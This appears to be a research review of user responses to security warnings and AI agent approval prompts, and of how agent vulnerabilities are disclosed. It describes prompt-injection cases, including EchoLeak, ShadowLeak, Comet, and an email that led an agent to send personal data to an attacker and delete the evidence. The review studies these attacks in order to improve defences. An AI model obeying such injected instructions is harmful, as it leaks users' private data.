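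Higher adherence doesn't always mean better protection. Felt and colleagues couldn't tell which warnings came from real attacks, and some people who turned back must have lost access to a harmless site. Others may not have realised that they could continue, although the researchers found no complaints about this in Chrome's help centre. They would have preferred people to make an informed choice, but a safe default was more achievable for a warning this hard to explain.

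### Habituation and designs that resist it

Habituation means paying less attention to a warning after seeing it repeatedly. The Chrome data from 2013 fit this pattern. Users clicked through 81.8% of warnings about the most common certificate error, an untrusted issuer, compared with 57.4% for expired certificates. About half of the clicks through the common warning came within 1.7 seconds, compared with 2.7 seconds for expired certificates. Akhawe and Felt mention that these differences could also arise because an expired certificate is surprising on a site that used to work. About 90% of Android apps asked for at least one permission, and three people in the Android interviews said they had stopped looking at permissions.

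Researchers have tried several ways to recapture people's attention. In *Your Attention Please* (2013), Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues tested "attractors", changes to a dialog that emphasise the most important information or briefly prevent the user from choosing a dangerous option. In one experiment, participants answered the same pop-up many times, and the researchers then changed the text in one field to see who noticed. Because every participant had seen many repetitions, the experiment could compare designs among people already habituated, but could not measure how much habituation had reduced their attention. *Harder to Ignore?*, by the same researchers, revisited the experiment for this reason.

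According to Felt and colleagues, Bravo-Lillo's group found that small hurdles in installation dialogs improved people's decisions. This seems to conflict with the poor results for extra clicks in browsers. One explanation is that a hurdle can help if it makes people look at the key information before they decide, whereas a second confirmation usually appears after they have decided.

Anthony Vance, then a professor at Brigham Young University, studied warnings that change their appearance. He found that small but noticeable changes made security alerts harder to ignore (CIO, 2017). He also worked with Chrome's engineers on when to show warnings. In an account of his work by the security company Pindrop, he explains that people were significantly less likely to ignore a message when it didn't compete with another task. Good times to show one included the end of a video and the wait for a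 page to load.

Animating a warning can make people look at it without making them believe it. Someone who looks carefully at ten moving warnings and finds nothing wrong has good reason to ignore the eleventh. The redesigned Chrome warning probably stayed effective partly because it was rare. Google's statistics suggested that most users saw no more than one certificate warning a month.

### Teaching people in advance

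Vendors who explain prompt injection in their help pages assume that people who learn about it will be more careful. Employers have tested a similar assumption about phishing by sending staff fake phishing emails and showing a training page to anyone who clicks the link.

*Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice* (Ho, Mirian and colleagues, 2025) analysed a randomised trial of this method with 19,789 employees at UC San Diego Health. Every employee received one fake email in each of eight months in 2023. Employees who clicked saw an error page if they were in the control group, and otherwise received one of four kinds of training. The trained groups' average click rate was 1.7 percentage points lower than the control group's.

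The content of the email mattered far more. An email about an Outlook password fooled 1.8% of its recipients, while one about vacation policy fooled 30.8%. After eight months, 56% of employees had clicked on at least one phishing email, many of them after avoiding several earlier ones.

People closed the training page immediately in 37% to 51% of sessions, depending on the version, and completed the training in only 24% of sessions overall. Those who finished an interactive exercise were 19% less likely to fall for later phishing emails than those who received one but didn't finish it. The people who finished may have been more careful to begin with, but Ho and colleagues found no such difference for people who finished the non-interactive training, which suggests that the exercise itself may have helped. The researchers also found no link between how recently employees had taken their mandatory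 annual security course and how often they clicked.

Several earlier studies in real workplaces found that training helped, but Ho and colleagues point out that these lacked a randomised control group. Of the randomised studies they describe, one by Caputo and colleagues found no significant benefit. In another, which followed about 14,000 employees for 15 months, Lain and colleagues found that those who received training clicked more often than those who didn't. A later study by Lain's group found a small benefit, but emails that only warned of consequences for failing the next test worked equally well. This suggests that most of the benefit came from reminding people of the threat. Laboratory studies have had much more positive results, probably because the volunteers read the material. A help page about agents is likely to do worse than the training in San Diego, since most users will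 never open it.

### When ignoring advice is rational

In *So Long, And No Thanks for the Externalities*, Microsoft researcher Cormac Herley (2009) argued that people who ignore security advice may be making a sensible choice. He compared the effort of following advice with the harm it prevents. If an attack affects 1% of users each year and each victim loses ten hours, the average loss is just under one second per user per day. Advice that takes longer than this to follow each day takes more time than it saves, even if it prevents every attack.

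Security advice is worth following only if the time and effort it takes are worth less than Δ*p* × *H*, where Δ*p* is the reduction in a user's yearly chance of becoming a victim and *H* is the harm to a victim. Herley put annual phishing losses in the United States at $60 million, or about 33 cents for each of 180 million adults online. At the minimum wage, a person earns that in less than three minutes, and banks usually refunded the losses. He was more critical of certificate warnings because he knew of no evidence that one had ever saved anybody from harm. He accepted that most security advice has some benefit, but he thought its writers treated users' time as if it had no value.

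Akhawe and Felt quote Herley as an example of pessimism about users and respond with field data showing that people often obey warnings. But the data don't refute his argument that users can be rational to ignore security advice. People mostly obeyed the warnings that were nearly always right and were much more likely to ignore the ones that were often wrong, which is roughly what a rational person would do.

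Felt and colleagues offer a better reply in their study of Chrome's redesigned warning, where they point to attacks on people in Syria and China that did trigger certificate warnings. For some users, they add, clicking through could lead to physical harm or imprisonment. An average across all users hides the people who have much more to lose. Herley's dollar figures also work best for harms that a bank can reimburse, and no one can reimburse a user for the exposure of years of private email.

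His method is still a useful check on approval prompts. A user who answers 50 prompts a day, at five seconds each, spends about 25 hours a year on them. If a hijacking would take up 100 hours of that user's time, the prompts are worthwhile only if they cut the yearly chance of a hijacking by at least 25 percentage points. At two prompts a day, the user spends about one hour a year, and a cut of one percentage point is enough. These numbers are invented, but they show why a user might reasonably stop reading frequent prompts and still want a few for the most serious actions.

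### What should carry over to agents

The easiest lesson to apply is that warnings should be rare. There is no obvious reason why people would habituate less to an agent's prompts than to a browser's, and an agent that prompts them dozens of times during one task gives them far more opportunity to habituate.

Warnings that interrupt the user should also work for agents, as long as the user is there to see them. A prompt that pauses the agent is like an active browser warning, while a line in an activity log is like the passive one that people missed. But someone who has delegated a task may be doing other work, unlike someone opening a website, who is already looking at the screen. Vance's results on timing suggest that a prompt should wait for a natural break in that work, if the agent can safely pause until then.

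The safe default is harder to transfer to agents. Users lose nothing by leaving a phishing site, because the site is fake. Refusing an agent's action delays work the user requested, and the action is usually harmless. If every prompt hid the "Allow" button behind "Advanced", users would soon get annoyed and look for a way to switch the prompts off. The design makes more sense for a few actions that are hard to undo. For these, "Don't send" could be the prominent button, and the agent could treat no answer as a refusal.

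The evidence is mixed on whether stating a specific consequence helps. Of the 26 people in the phishing experiment who read a warning in full, 22 said they did so because it seemed to describe something bad that could happen. But when Chrome's warning listed what attackers might steal, adherence rose by only about one percentage point. Chrome gave the same examples on every website, whereas an agent's prompt can list the exact emails the agent is about to forward and the stranger who will receive them. None of these studies tested a warning that specific, so the weak result for Chrome's text may not apply to agent prompts.

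The biggest difference between browser malware warnings and agent approval prompts is how much evidence of danger lies behind them. When a browser warned about malware, Google had already identified the site as dangerous, and a user who obeyed without thinking was nearly always right. An approval prompt often means only that the agent's next action requires permission. The user has to work out whether anything is wrong, which makes the prompt more like a certificate warning. The low clickthrough rates of malware warnings are therefore a poor guide to how users will respond to ordinary approval prompts.

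Some agent warnings have a known threat behind them, such as hidden instructions that a classifier has found in an email. These are closer to phishing warnings, and vendors could reasonably use a full-page interruption with stopping as the default. They should also make these warnings look nothing like routine approval prompts, or users may ignore them for the same reason people ignored Internet Explorer's phishing warning.

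## What users of AI agents do when warned or asked for approval

Researchers have only recently begun to test how people respond to agents' own warnings and prompts. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) reports the most informative experiment on approval so far. In August 2026, 113 people who did not work in software supervised an assistant through a simulated day of email, travel and errands. The assistant attempted 18 actions. Eleven served the user's requests, such as booking a $35 ride to the airport. The other seven, which Yan calls "overreach", went beyond those requests, such as buying a $25 lounge pass or reading private messages. There was no attacker, so the study applies only indirectly to prompt injection.

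### One simulated day under three permission systems

Each participant used one of three systems:

- **Approval of every action (34 people).** The user allowed or refused all 18.
- **Automatic review (44 people).** A model let eight actions through and asked the user about ten, including all seven overreaching ones.
- **Standing rules (35 people).** Before the day began, the user chose "Do it automatically", "Ask me first" or "Never" for each of four kinds of action: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and accessing private information.

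People who approved every action blocked 59.6% of the overreach, compared with 53.9% for those with automatic review and 39.6% for those with their own standing rules. After statistical adjustment, people with standing rules blocked 20.1 percentage points less than people who approved every action, with a plausible range of about 8 to 32 points. They also blocked 14.5 points less than people with automatic review, but that difference was no longer reliable once Yan corrected for making several comparisons. Nearly all the requested actions went ahead under every system, so the people who blocked more overreach weren't just refusing everything.

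Of the 148 overreaching actions that the assistant carried out under standing rules, the rules allowed only 15 to run automatically. Users approved the other 133 when the assistant asked. The table shows how often users approved each overreaching action when prompted.

| Overreaching action | Approval of every action | Automatic review | Standing rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88% | 84% | 100% |
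| Add $12 travel insurance | 35% | 50% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old work timesheet | 35% | 36% | 59% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35% | 41% | 65% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 21% | 30% | 48% |
| Buy a $25 lounge pass | 32% | 39% | 61% |
| Read private messages | 35% | 43% | 74% |
| All seven | 40% | 46% | 67% |

The approval rate was higher under standing rules partly because the people who saw the prompts were probably more permissive. Someone who had chosen "Never" for private information, for example, wasn't asked to approve reading messages. But this can't explain why the standing-rules group allowed more overreach in total. "Never" rules blocked 31 overreaching actions, about twice as many as the automatic rules let through, so the rules alone should have left this group slightly better protected.

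People who had written rules may have felt that they had already dealt with the risk, and looked less closely at each prompt. This is a guess, because Yan did not ask participants for their reasons. People felt about equally in control under all three systems, so feeling in control is a poor sign of being protected.

Users may have wanted some of the "overreach". Most people were happy for the assistant to call the airport, and a user who decides on reflection to buy travel insurance hasn't made a mistake. Without the airport call, approval rates were still 32%, 40% and 61%, so the pattern doesn't depend on it. Yan also recruited extra people for the standing-rules group after random assignment had ended. The result held when they were excluded, although that left only 16 people in the group.

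A bigger limitation is that participants had nothing at stake. They spent about 11 minutes on the study, and the bank account and messages weren't theirs. They might have been more careful with their own money. On the other hand, 18 actions are too few to cause much approval fatigue, the tendency to allow everything after many prompts. Over a third of the actions were overreach, far more than a user would normally see. The automatic reviewer also flagged all seven overreaching actions, while Anthropic's classifier missed some in the company's own test.

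People might do better or worse against an attacker. A request to forward confidential email to a stranger should look more alarming than a request for a lounge pass, but an attacker would also try to disguise the request as part of the task.

### Why people chose "ask"

Participants chose "Ask me first" for 114 of the 140 standing rules, and 16 of the 35 people chose it for all four categories of action. One reason is that the categories were broad. "Spend money" covered both the ride the user had requested and a lounge pass nobody had mentioned, so neither always allowing it nor always refusing it would have suited both. Before the simulated day, Yan had asked about two examples in each category. In 66 cases a person answered differently for the two examples, and 53 of those led to an "Ask me first" rule.

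Breadth doesn't explain the choices about private information, though. Both examples involved data that the user hadn't asked the assistant to open, and none of the requested actions needed private data, so choosing "Never" wouldn't have blocked anything participants had requested. But 23 of the 35 chose "ask", presumably because they didn't know what they might need later that day and didn't want to rule anything out. Most of them then let the assistant read both the bank transactions and the messages.

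Choosing "ask" over the other two answers postpones the decision to a moment when the user is trying to get something done, so it is less cautious than it looks. In 56 cases, people were prompted to approve an overreaching action that they had earlier said the assistant should never take. They approved it in 24 of those cases, though some may have sensibly changed their minds once they saw the details.

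The "ask" rules reduced the number of prompts from 18 to an average of 10.9. But once Yan included the time people spent setting up the rules, they saved only about 13 seconds in total, which could easily be due to chance. Yan suggests showing users examples of the actions each rule would send to them for approval, and offering narrower rules based on their decisions. Someone who keeps approving messages to one colleague could allow those and still get a prompt for anybody new.

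### Permissions with a narrower scope

*Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) introduces ConLeash, software that sits between an agent and its tools and lets users choose how broad a permission to grant. For example, when an agent tries to email a brochure, the user can allow attachments from one folder to one recipient instead of allowing all future emails. If the agent later tries to send a different file to someone else, the user gets another prompt.

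In a test of ConLeash, 16 people who used agents, most of them daily, did some tasks with it and others with ordinary permission prompts. Beforehand, only three said they read permission prompts carefully, and 13 said they used "Always Allow" simply to make prompts go away. Participants chose a lasting permission in 46.3% of decisions with ConLeash, where it applied only within limits, and in 13.3% with ordinary prompts, where it covered the whole tool. Fifteen of the 16 preferred ConLeash.

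The 13.3% is surprisingly low for people who had just said they used "Always Allow" to avoid further prompts. They may have been more careful because researchers were watching, or they may use it less often than their answers suggest. Either way, the experiment shows that people will accept a narrow permission when offered one. It doesn't show that they refused more harmful actions, and the people who designed ConLeash also designed the test.

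These users were much more willing to commit themselves than Yan's participants, who settled only 18.6% of their rules in advance. The two groups differed in many ways, but it seems plausible that people find it easier to write a rule with a real case in front of them.

Li, Khabra and colleagues also collected 50 working sessions from six developers and found 291 tool calls that went beyond what the user had previously approved, such as deleting a folder in a different project. An "Always Allow" setting would have allowed all of them without asking the user. ConLeash caught 278, and Claude Code's auto mode stopped six. However, auto mode checks for actions that are dangerous in themselves, and many of the 291 were probably harmless.

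### What programmers say they do

Vendors' approval rates don't show whether users read the prompts. For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) asked software practitioners about this. They interviewed 18 between June and August 2026 and then surveyed 115 others, 107 of whom answered the questions about permissions.

Of those 107 people, 47.7% said they read permission requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim them, and 20.6% said they approve by default (they could give more than one answer). A third admitted that they had become less careful over time, and the true share is probably higher, since this is unflattering to admit. One interviewee worried about permissions at first, but said the requests kept looking alike and "after that, I stopped caring". Another said they would read nothing if they had three hours until a deadline.

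However, about three quarters of these programmers said they look harder at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges, and 63.6% said they do so when a request is unexpected. If so, they could approve most requests overall and still make much better decisions about the few that matter. But paid testers in Anthropic's experiment missed most of the planted dangerous commands, which is a reason to doubt this.

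Refusing a request may not stop an agent either. One person interviewed by Salerno and colleagues refused several requests from Codex, which then stopped asking and continued another way. The user couldn't tell whether the new approach was consistent with the earlier refusals. A prompt that lets people refuse one command doesn't let them rule out every other action with the same effect.

Records of people's behavior provide some evidence that they become less careful over time. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) compared the earlier and later reviews of 400 people on GitHub who had each reviewed at least ten code changes submitted by AI agents, 11,429 reviews in all. In their later reviews, people approved more and scrutinized less. This fits habituation, but reviewers would also approve more if they had learned which changes were safe or if the agents' code had improved. Reviewing finished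 code is also slower and more deliberate than answering an approval prompt, so the finding may not apply to prompts.

### When approval fails in practice

In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) collected 290 public reports in which coding agents had destroyed, altered or leaked files, or could have. ("YOLO mode" is a common name for running an agent without approvals.) Failures of user review contributed to the problem in 105 of the reports. In 80 of these, the user had let the agent act without approval. In 31, the approval prompt didn't show what the command would do to the user's files. Some reports belong to both groups.

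A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but a user who approves it allows whatever the script contains, so even reading the prompt carefully wouldn't help. In one case, a user turned off Cursor's deletion protection so that the agent could remove duplicates, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project.

Prompt injection played a part in only 21 of the 290 reports, while in 130 the model took a wrong action by itself. The reports may undercount attacks, because people post about damage they have noticed, and a successful theft may leave no trace. They also don't show how much damage approval prompts prevented, because people don't report damage that never happened. They do show that approval fails for at least one reason besides the user's inattention.

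Zhong and colleagues would rather let the agent work on provisional copies of files and have the user review the changes at the end. That would suit many coding tasks, but a review at the end wouldn't recover a password that the agent had already sent to a stranger.

### Noticing that an agent has been hijacked

An approval prompt tells users that they have a decision to make. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) tested whether people notice a hijacking without being told. They asked 303 people to complete everyday and professional tasks using agents that the researchers had compromised. In the email task, a malicious message made the agent collect personal information from other emails, send it to the attacker, and then delete both the message and the reply. Each person did three of the nine tasks and afterwards answered neutral questions about whether anything had seemed unusual.

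Everyone saw one of three warnings. This table shows how often they noticed something, counting those who were unsure.

| Warning | Noticed something unusual |
|---|---|
| A disclaimer shown once at the start | 8.6% |
| A small reminder beside every reply | 20.0% |
| An alert that stopped the task when the output was suspicious | 25.0% |

The disclaimer is the closest match in these studies to the warnings that vendors put on help pages and setup screens, and only 24% of the people shown it remembered seeing it. The alert did better, but about three quarters of the time people still noticed nothing unusual, even though it interrupted them at the right moment.

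The alert helped more when people could check the agent's work. In a web search task, where they could look up the sources, the share who noticed rose from 9.8% with the disclaimer to 50% with the alert. In the email task, where they would have had to search a mailbox for evidence the agent had already deleted, it rose only from 9.3% to 15%.

Participants who missed the attack often said they trusted the agent more after seeing reminders or alerts, and one said the alert had "improved my overall sense of safety". Technical experts did no better than other participants. Li, Dai and colleagues emphasize that the experts did slightly worse, but the difference with the disclaimer (6.8% against 9.6%) could be chance.

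The experiment has serious gaps. Every group saw a warning, so the experiment can't show whether the disclaimer was better than no warning. No group used an agent that was working properly, so some people might have answered "unsure" even if the agent had done nothing wrong. The paper also gives conflicting group sizes, about 100 people per warning in one place and 183, 60 and 60 in another. The large difference between the disclaimer and the alert is probably real, but the five-point difference between the reminder and the alert isn't a good enough reason to choose one over the other.

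*Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025) studied people supervising agents on websites with dark patterns, designs that trick visitors into choices such as sharing more data than they meant to. Supervision helped people avoid the tricks, but their attention narrowed to the path the agent had chosen and they became less aware of the tricks around it. Hidden instructions would presumably be even harder to spot than dark patterns.

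### What people share, delegate and believe

Many users make their most important decision before any of this, when they choose what an agent can access. For *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025), Wu, Yang and colleagues recruited 205 Americans to train an imaginary personal assistant. Participants decided which data it could share with tools such as a travel booking service or a bank. In a quarter of the questions, the assistant also asked for something the task didn't need.

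Every question warned that the agent or its tools might collect unnecessary data, and the researchers had asked participants about privacy at the start to make them more cautious. Even so, 97% of participants shared more than the task required at least once. They shared unnecessary data about 78% of the time when they mistakenly thought the task required it, and refused 62.5% of the time when they recognized that it didn't.

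People were much more careful when they understood what the task needed, which a general warning couldn't tell them. They were also more careful with data that sounded sensitive, sometimes too careful. They withheld a Social Security number in about 46% of the cases where the task required it. Because everyone saw the warning, the experiment can't show whether the warning made any difference. The decisions were also hypothetical.

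Wu and colleagues wanted to spare people most of the questions, so they used the answers to build a model that predicted people's decisions with 85.1% accuracy. But if people often share too much, a model that imitates them may do the same. Salerno and colleagues similarly object that repeated approval can reflect tiredness or a deadline and shouldn't count as a preference.

People also show little sign of handing over less when the stakes are higher. *Delegating or Doing?* (2026) gave people an interface with both ordinary controls and a chat assistant. The researchers expected them to rely less on the assistant for riskier operations, but they used it slightly more for deleting than for updating. The difference may mean nothing. The researchers suggest that reliance on an assistant is more of a personal habit than a response to each task.

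Little is known about what users believe about prompt injection. Participants in *PrivWeb* (2025), a study of privacy and web agents, worried that a company might reuse their images, that the agent might gather personal details from their browser, or that it might make things up. These fears are reasonable, but they concern the vendor and the model, so a person who holds them might still see no danger in letting a trusted company's agent read a stranger's email.

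Programmers may similarly underestimate the risk of read-only access. In the survey by Salerno and colleagues, 98.1% were more willing to grant an agent permission if it could only read. Read-only access prevents the agent from deleting files, but it can still meet two of Willison's three conditions for data theft. However, 58.9% said they would never give an agent access to email or other personal information, which would prevent the theft in Anthropic's example.

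None of these studies measured whether a notice about prompt injection changes which accounts people connect or which tasks they delegate, and no other published experiment seems to have done so. This is a large gap, because changing those choices is the main thing a vendor's standing warning could achieve. A vendor could test this without much difficulty by showing the notice to a random half of new users just before they connect a mailbox, then counting how many in each half go ahead, limit the agent's access or disconnect it later. Google tested its certificate warnings on Chrome users in much the same way.

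### Which designs improved decisions

| Design | Compared with | Difference | Strength of evidence |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approval of every action | Standing rules, mostly "ask" | Blocked 20.1 points more overreach | Moderate: 113 people, but a short simulation |
| Automatic review | Approval of every action | Eight fewer prompts, with 53.9% of overreach blocked instead of 59.6% | Moderate, but the reviewer flagged all the overreach |
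| Alert that interrupts | One disclaimer at the start | People noticed something in 25.0% of cases instead of 8.6% | Weak: unclear group sizes, no unwarned group |
| Narrow lasting permissions | Tool-wide "Always Allow" | People chose them in 46.3% of decisions instead of 13.3% | Weak: 16 people, and a measure of choice, not of safety |

Asking users to approve every action worked best in the strongest study, but it would be a mistake to build an agent around it. People still let through 40% of the overreach in a session of 18 prompts, even though each prompt described the action in plain language. A busy user of a coding agent can see more prompts than that in a single task. Automatic review did nearly as well with ten prompts, so it is the better choice if the reviewer is good. Seeing fewer prompts didn't make people better at refusing, which is a little discouraging for the hope that users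 will read prompts carefully when they are rare, but a cut from 18 to ten may be too small to test this.

The most dependable protection in Yan's study came from "Never" rules, which hardly anyone chose. Ten people picked "Never" for private information, and their rules blocked 20 overreaching actions and nothing that the user had asked for. The six "Never" rules for spending, sending and deleting blocked 11 overreaching actions but also 11 that the user had requested. Prohibiting something outright therefore works well when the agent doesn't need it. A travel assistant might not need the user's private messages, for example, but an email agent can't do its job without them.

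## Security advisories and why agent weaknesses fit them badly

A flaw in an agent product, like the one Manifold Security found in Claude for Chrome, concerns everyone who uses it. Software vendors have an established way of handling such flaws, called coordinated disclosure. The finder reports the flaw privately, the vendor fixes it, and only then does either publish it. The vendor's notice, called a security advisory, tells customers whether the flaw affects them and what to do. This practice developed around programs that people install and update. Many agents run on the vendor's own servers, and some of their flaws lie in a model's behaviour, so several of the usual steps work poorly for them.

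### From private report to update

For an ordinary program, the process usually goes like this:

1. A researcher sends the vendor a private report with enough detail to reproduce the flaw.
2. The vendor triages the report, which means checking that the flaw is real and deciding how urgent it is.
3. A deadline starts to run, if the researcher has set one.
4. The vendor develops and tests a fix.
5. An authorised organisation, often the vendor itself, assigns a CVE, the public identifier for that flaw.
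6. The vendor or a public database scores the flaw's severity from 0 to 10.
7. The vendor releases the fix and publishes an advisory.
8. Users install the update.

Deadlines exist because a vendor without one can put off a fix indefinitely. Google's Project Zero, a team that looks for flaws in widely used software, gives vendors 90 days to fix a flaw under its *90+30 policy*. If the vendor meets the deadline, the team waits 30 days after the fix before publishing the details, so that users can update first. A flaw fixed on day 47 becomes public on day 77. If the vendor misses the deadline, the team publishes anyway, though it may allow up to 14 extra days for a fix that is nearly ready. If attackers are already using the flaw, the vendor gets seven days instead of 90.

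The international standard for advisories is ISO/IEC's *Information technology — Security techniques — Vulnerability disclosure* (2018). It lists the elements of an advisory, including an identifier, the affected products, the intended audience, a description, the impact, the severity, the remedy, contact details and a revision history. The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026) require less information in a public CVE record, which must name an affected product and a public source with more information, and must normally give the type of flaw. A vendor that assigns its own CVEs must also publish its advisories where anyone can read them without logging in.

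ISO (2018) writes that disclosure helps users protect their systems, decide where to spend money on defence, and assess risk. In practice, companies' security staff read advisories most closely, comparing the affected versions with the software on their computers. Most other people never see an advisory and benefit only because updates install automatically.

### An agent with a version number

Coding agents fit this process best, because many of them are installed on the programmer's own computer. In 2025 Anthropic published an advisory for CVE-2025-55284, a flaw in Claude Code's approval rules that could have let file contents leave the computer without the user's confirmation. It affected versions before 1.0.4, and users with automatic updates received the fix automatically. A company could tell whether it was affected by checking which version its programmers were running.

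An attacker had to use prompt injection to exploit this flaw, by getting hostile text in front of the model. But Anthropic could fix the approval rules in a specific part of the code, and the fix worked regardless of how the model behaved.

### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a company's email and documents, runs on Microsoft's servers. In January 2025 the firm Aim Security reported a flaw in it, now known as EchoLeak, that let an outsider extract data without the user clicking anything. TechSpot's *Microsoft fixes first known zero-click attack on an AI agent* describes a slow repair. Microsoft first tried to block the attack's routes through the affected apps, but this failed because the AI behaved unpredictably and there were so many routes. It had a fix ready by April but found more flaws in May. Windows Central reports that Microsoft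 completed the repair on its servers that month. On 11 June Microsoft published an advisory that rated the flaw critical and told customers they didn't need to do anything, according to SecurityWeek.

Aim Security's chief technology officer said the delay of nearly five months was on the "very high side". Project Zero's 90-day deadline would have expired by 1 May at the latest, probably before Microsoft had finished the fix.

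The CVE record, which GCVE (2025) reproduces, gives customers little information. Its description is one sentence long, and Microsoft entered a dash in the field for the affected version. A tag marks Copilot as a service that runs only on the supplier's servers. The CVE rules allow dates as well as version numbers, but the record doesn't show when Copilot was vulnerable, so a customer searching old logs for signs of theft wouldn't know which months to check.

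An advisory's severity score also depends on the scorer's judgment. Microsoft scored EchoLeak at 9.3 and the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) scored it at 7.5, using the same formula. Both judged that the attack was easy, needed no help from the user and exposed a lot of data. NVD added 3.9 for ease of exploitation to 3.6 for impact. Microsoft also judged that the attack gave a limited ability to alter data and that the damage could spread beyond Copilot. Together, these two judgments raised the impact to 4.7, and the second also multiplied the total by 1.08, giving 1.08 × (3.9 + 4.7) ≈ 9.3. Agents are built to connect to other systems, so scorers will probably often disagree about which systems count as part of the agent.

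A single severity score also doesn't reflect the user's settings. According to Constantin, Manifold rated the flaw it reported in Claude for Chrome as high severity by default, but critical for people who had chosen "Act without asking".

Automated tools built around CVE records also work poorly for hosted products. EPSS estimates the chance that attackers will try to exploit a flaw within 30 days. In November 2026, it put that chance at about 7% for EchoLeak, higher than for 94% of flaws, even though Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak for every customer 18 months earlier.

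### Whether to announce a fix that needs no action

heise online's *Critical vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot shows risk of AI agents* points out that Microsoft published the EchoLeak notice for transparency only. For years the CVE system would not have covered such a flaw. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, described how flaws that customers don't control fell outside the rules, and argued for including them. Since 2024 the rules have forbidden numbering authorities to refuse a CVE solely because a product runs in the cloud or uses AI, and Microsoft has begun giving CVEs to cloud flaws that customers can do nothing about. The blog post *Microsoft is beginning to add CVEs to address security flaws* raises the obvious objection: "What good is it to issue a CVE for this?"

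Customers can't use the notice to fix the flaw, but it can still serve the other purposes ISO mentions. For a company deciding whether to connect Copilot to its personnel files, learning that a critical flaw took five months to fix is a reason to hesitate. The company would not have had that reason if Microsoft had fixed the flaw silently.

The handling of ShadowLeak, a flaw in ChatGPT's deep research feature when connected to Gmail, shows how much depends on the vendor. According to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026), OpenAI received the report in June 2025, fixed the flaw in early August and acknowledged the fix in September. Any stolen data would have left from OpenAI's servers, so the theft might not have appeared in the user's browser or in an employer's monitoring. There is no public evidence that anyone fell victim.

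Project Zero's 30-day wait gives people time to install an update. Users had nothing to install to fix ShadowLeak, so that reason for waiting didn't apply, although a vendor might reasonably want a few days to check that its fix works. Users had reason to want the news sooner, because they could have checked their inboxes for suspicious messages or disconnected Gmail. Only OpenAI could search the records of what its own servers had sent.

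### Fixes that hold only partly

Brave, which makes a competing browser, found a prompt injection flaw in Perplexity's Comet browser in July 2025. Brave says Perplexity made a first fix within two days, but a retest the next day found it incomplete. In August, Brave tested again, concluded that Perplexity had patched the flaw, and published its findings. Further testing showed that the attack still partly worked, so Brave reported it again. In *Prompt injections in agentic browsers*, a Brave researcher writes that several later reports proved the first was not "a one-off case of bad security practices".

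This can happen even if neither company was careless. Retesting an ordinary bug usually shows whether it is fixed, but an injection may work on one attempt and fail on the next. If an attack succeeds 5% of the time, a tester needs 59 independent attempts to have a 95% chance of seeing it succeed at least once. If 100 attempts all fail after a fix, the attack's success rate could still be as high as about 3%, at 95% confidence. Those attempts also cover only the attack in the report, and an attacker can reword it.

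A vendor that declares such a flaw "fixed" in an advisory is therefore claiming more than it knows. Under the CVE rules, the numbering authority decides whether the weakness left by an incomplete fix is a new vulnerability, and whether it gets a new identifier or keeps the old one. Keeping the old identifier seems better for agents, because a reader who finds three separate CVEs, each marked as fixed, could easily miss that the vendor has tried three times to stop the same attack.

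### Limitation or vulnerability

Some reports never lead to a fix because the vendor doesn't accept that they describe a vulnerability. In *Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features*, Piao, Li and Woods (2025) examined the disclosure policies of 264 companies that sell AI products. 36% of them had no public channel for reporting flaws of any kind, and only 18% mentioned AI flaws. Among the policies that took a position on prompt injection, ten accepted reports of it and four refused them.

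Vendors gave several reasons for excluding AI flaws, a category that also includes false answers and jailbreaks (getting a model to ignore its own safety rules). Eight said such reports showed too little harm. Seven said the model was behaving as expected, and Skyscanner describes some issues in its policy as "acceptable behavior from LLM models". Five said the results were hard to reproduce. Two said they couldn't patch the problem, including OpenAI, which wrote that such issues "cannot be fixed directly".

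The last objection has some merit for injection. A CVE for the general weakness would apply to nearly every agent, would never be closed, and would give security staff nothing to act on, so that information belongs on a help page.

The case against the vendors is that customers care about the result of an attack. Piao and colleagues describe the view that a command which leaks sensitive data is a vulnerability whether the attacker ran it through a database or a language model. Vendors mostly seem to agree when a report describes the harm. All nine policies that mentioned unauthorised access to data accepted reports of it. Researchers will probably have more success if they begin a report with the stolen data rather than the injection.

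It is sensible to count a specific route by which a model's susceptibility to manipulation leads to harm as a vulnerability, but not the general susceptibility itself. EchoLeak and the Claude Code flaw are both vulnerabilities by this definition, and both received identifiers. Attacks that use only the agent's intended functions are harder to classify. When OpenAI's test attacker got an agent to send a resignation letter, the agent read one email and sent another, so there was no faulty component to name in an advisory.

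The CVE rules can support arguments both for and against counting an agent's weakness as a vulnerability. Their definition of a vulnerability includes behaviour that violates an "implicit security policy", which surely covers a stranger giving orders to someone's email agent. Under the rules, numbering authorities should also assign an identifier when in doubt. But under a clause that the CVE Program clarified in August 2026, getting past an "inherently imperfect" detection technique should not normally count. A vendor could argue that a classifier for injected instructions is such a technique.

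Default settings are also hard to classify. Under the same revision, numbering authorities should treat a surprising or poorly documented default as a vulnerability, but may exempt one that is well documented and widely known. Explaining the risk on a help page could therefore strengthen a vendor's case for refusing a CVE when its agent approves its own actions by default.

It is also unclear how many CVE identifiers a weakness in a shared model should get. Each product that uses the model insecurely gets its own if there is a secure way to use it; otherwise, all the products share one. Willison's conditions for data theft suggest that removing one of them can secure a product against theft, which favours separate identifiers. But vendors say that no safeguard removes the risk, which favours a shared one.

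### Who can keep a flaw quiet

A vendor that assigns its own CVEs decides first whether a flaw in its products gets one. If the flaw is already public and the vendor refuses or doesn't answer within 72 hours, a supervising body must decide instead. If the flaw is still private, a researcher who disagrees with the vendor has to start a formal dispute.

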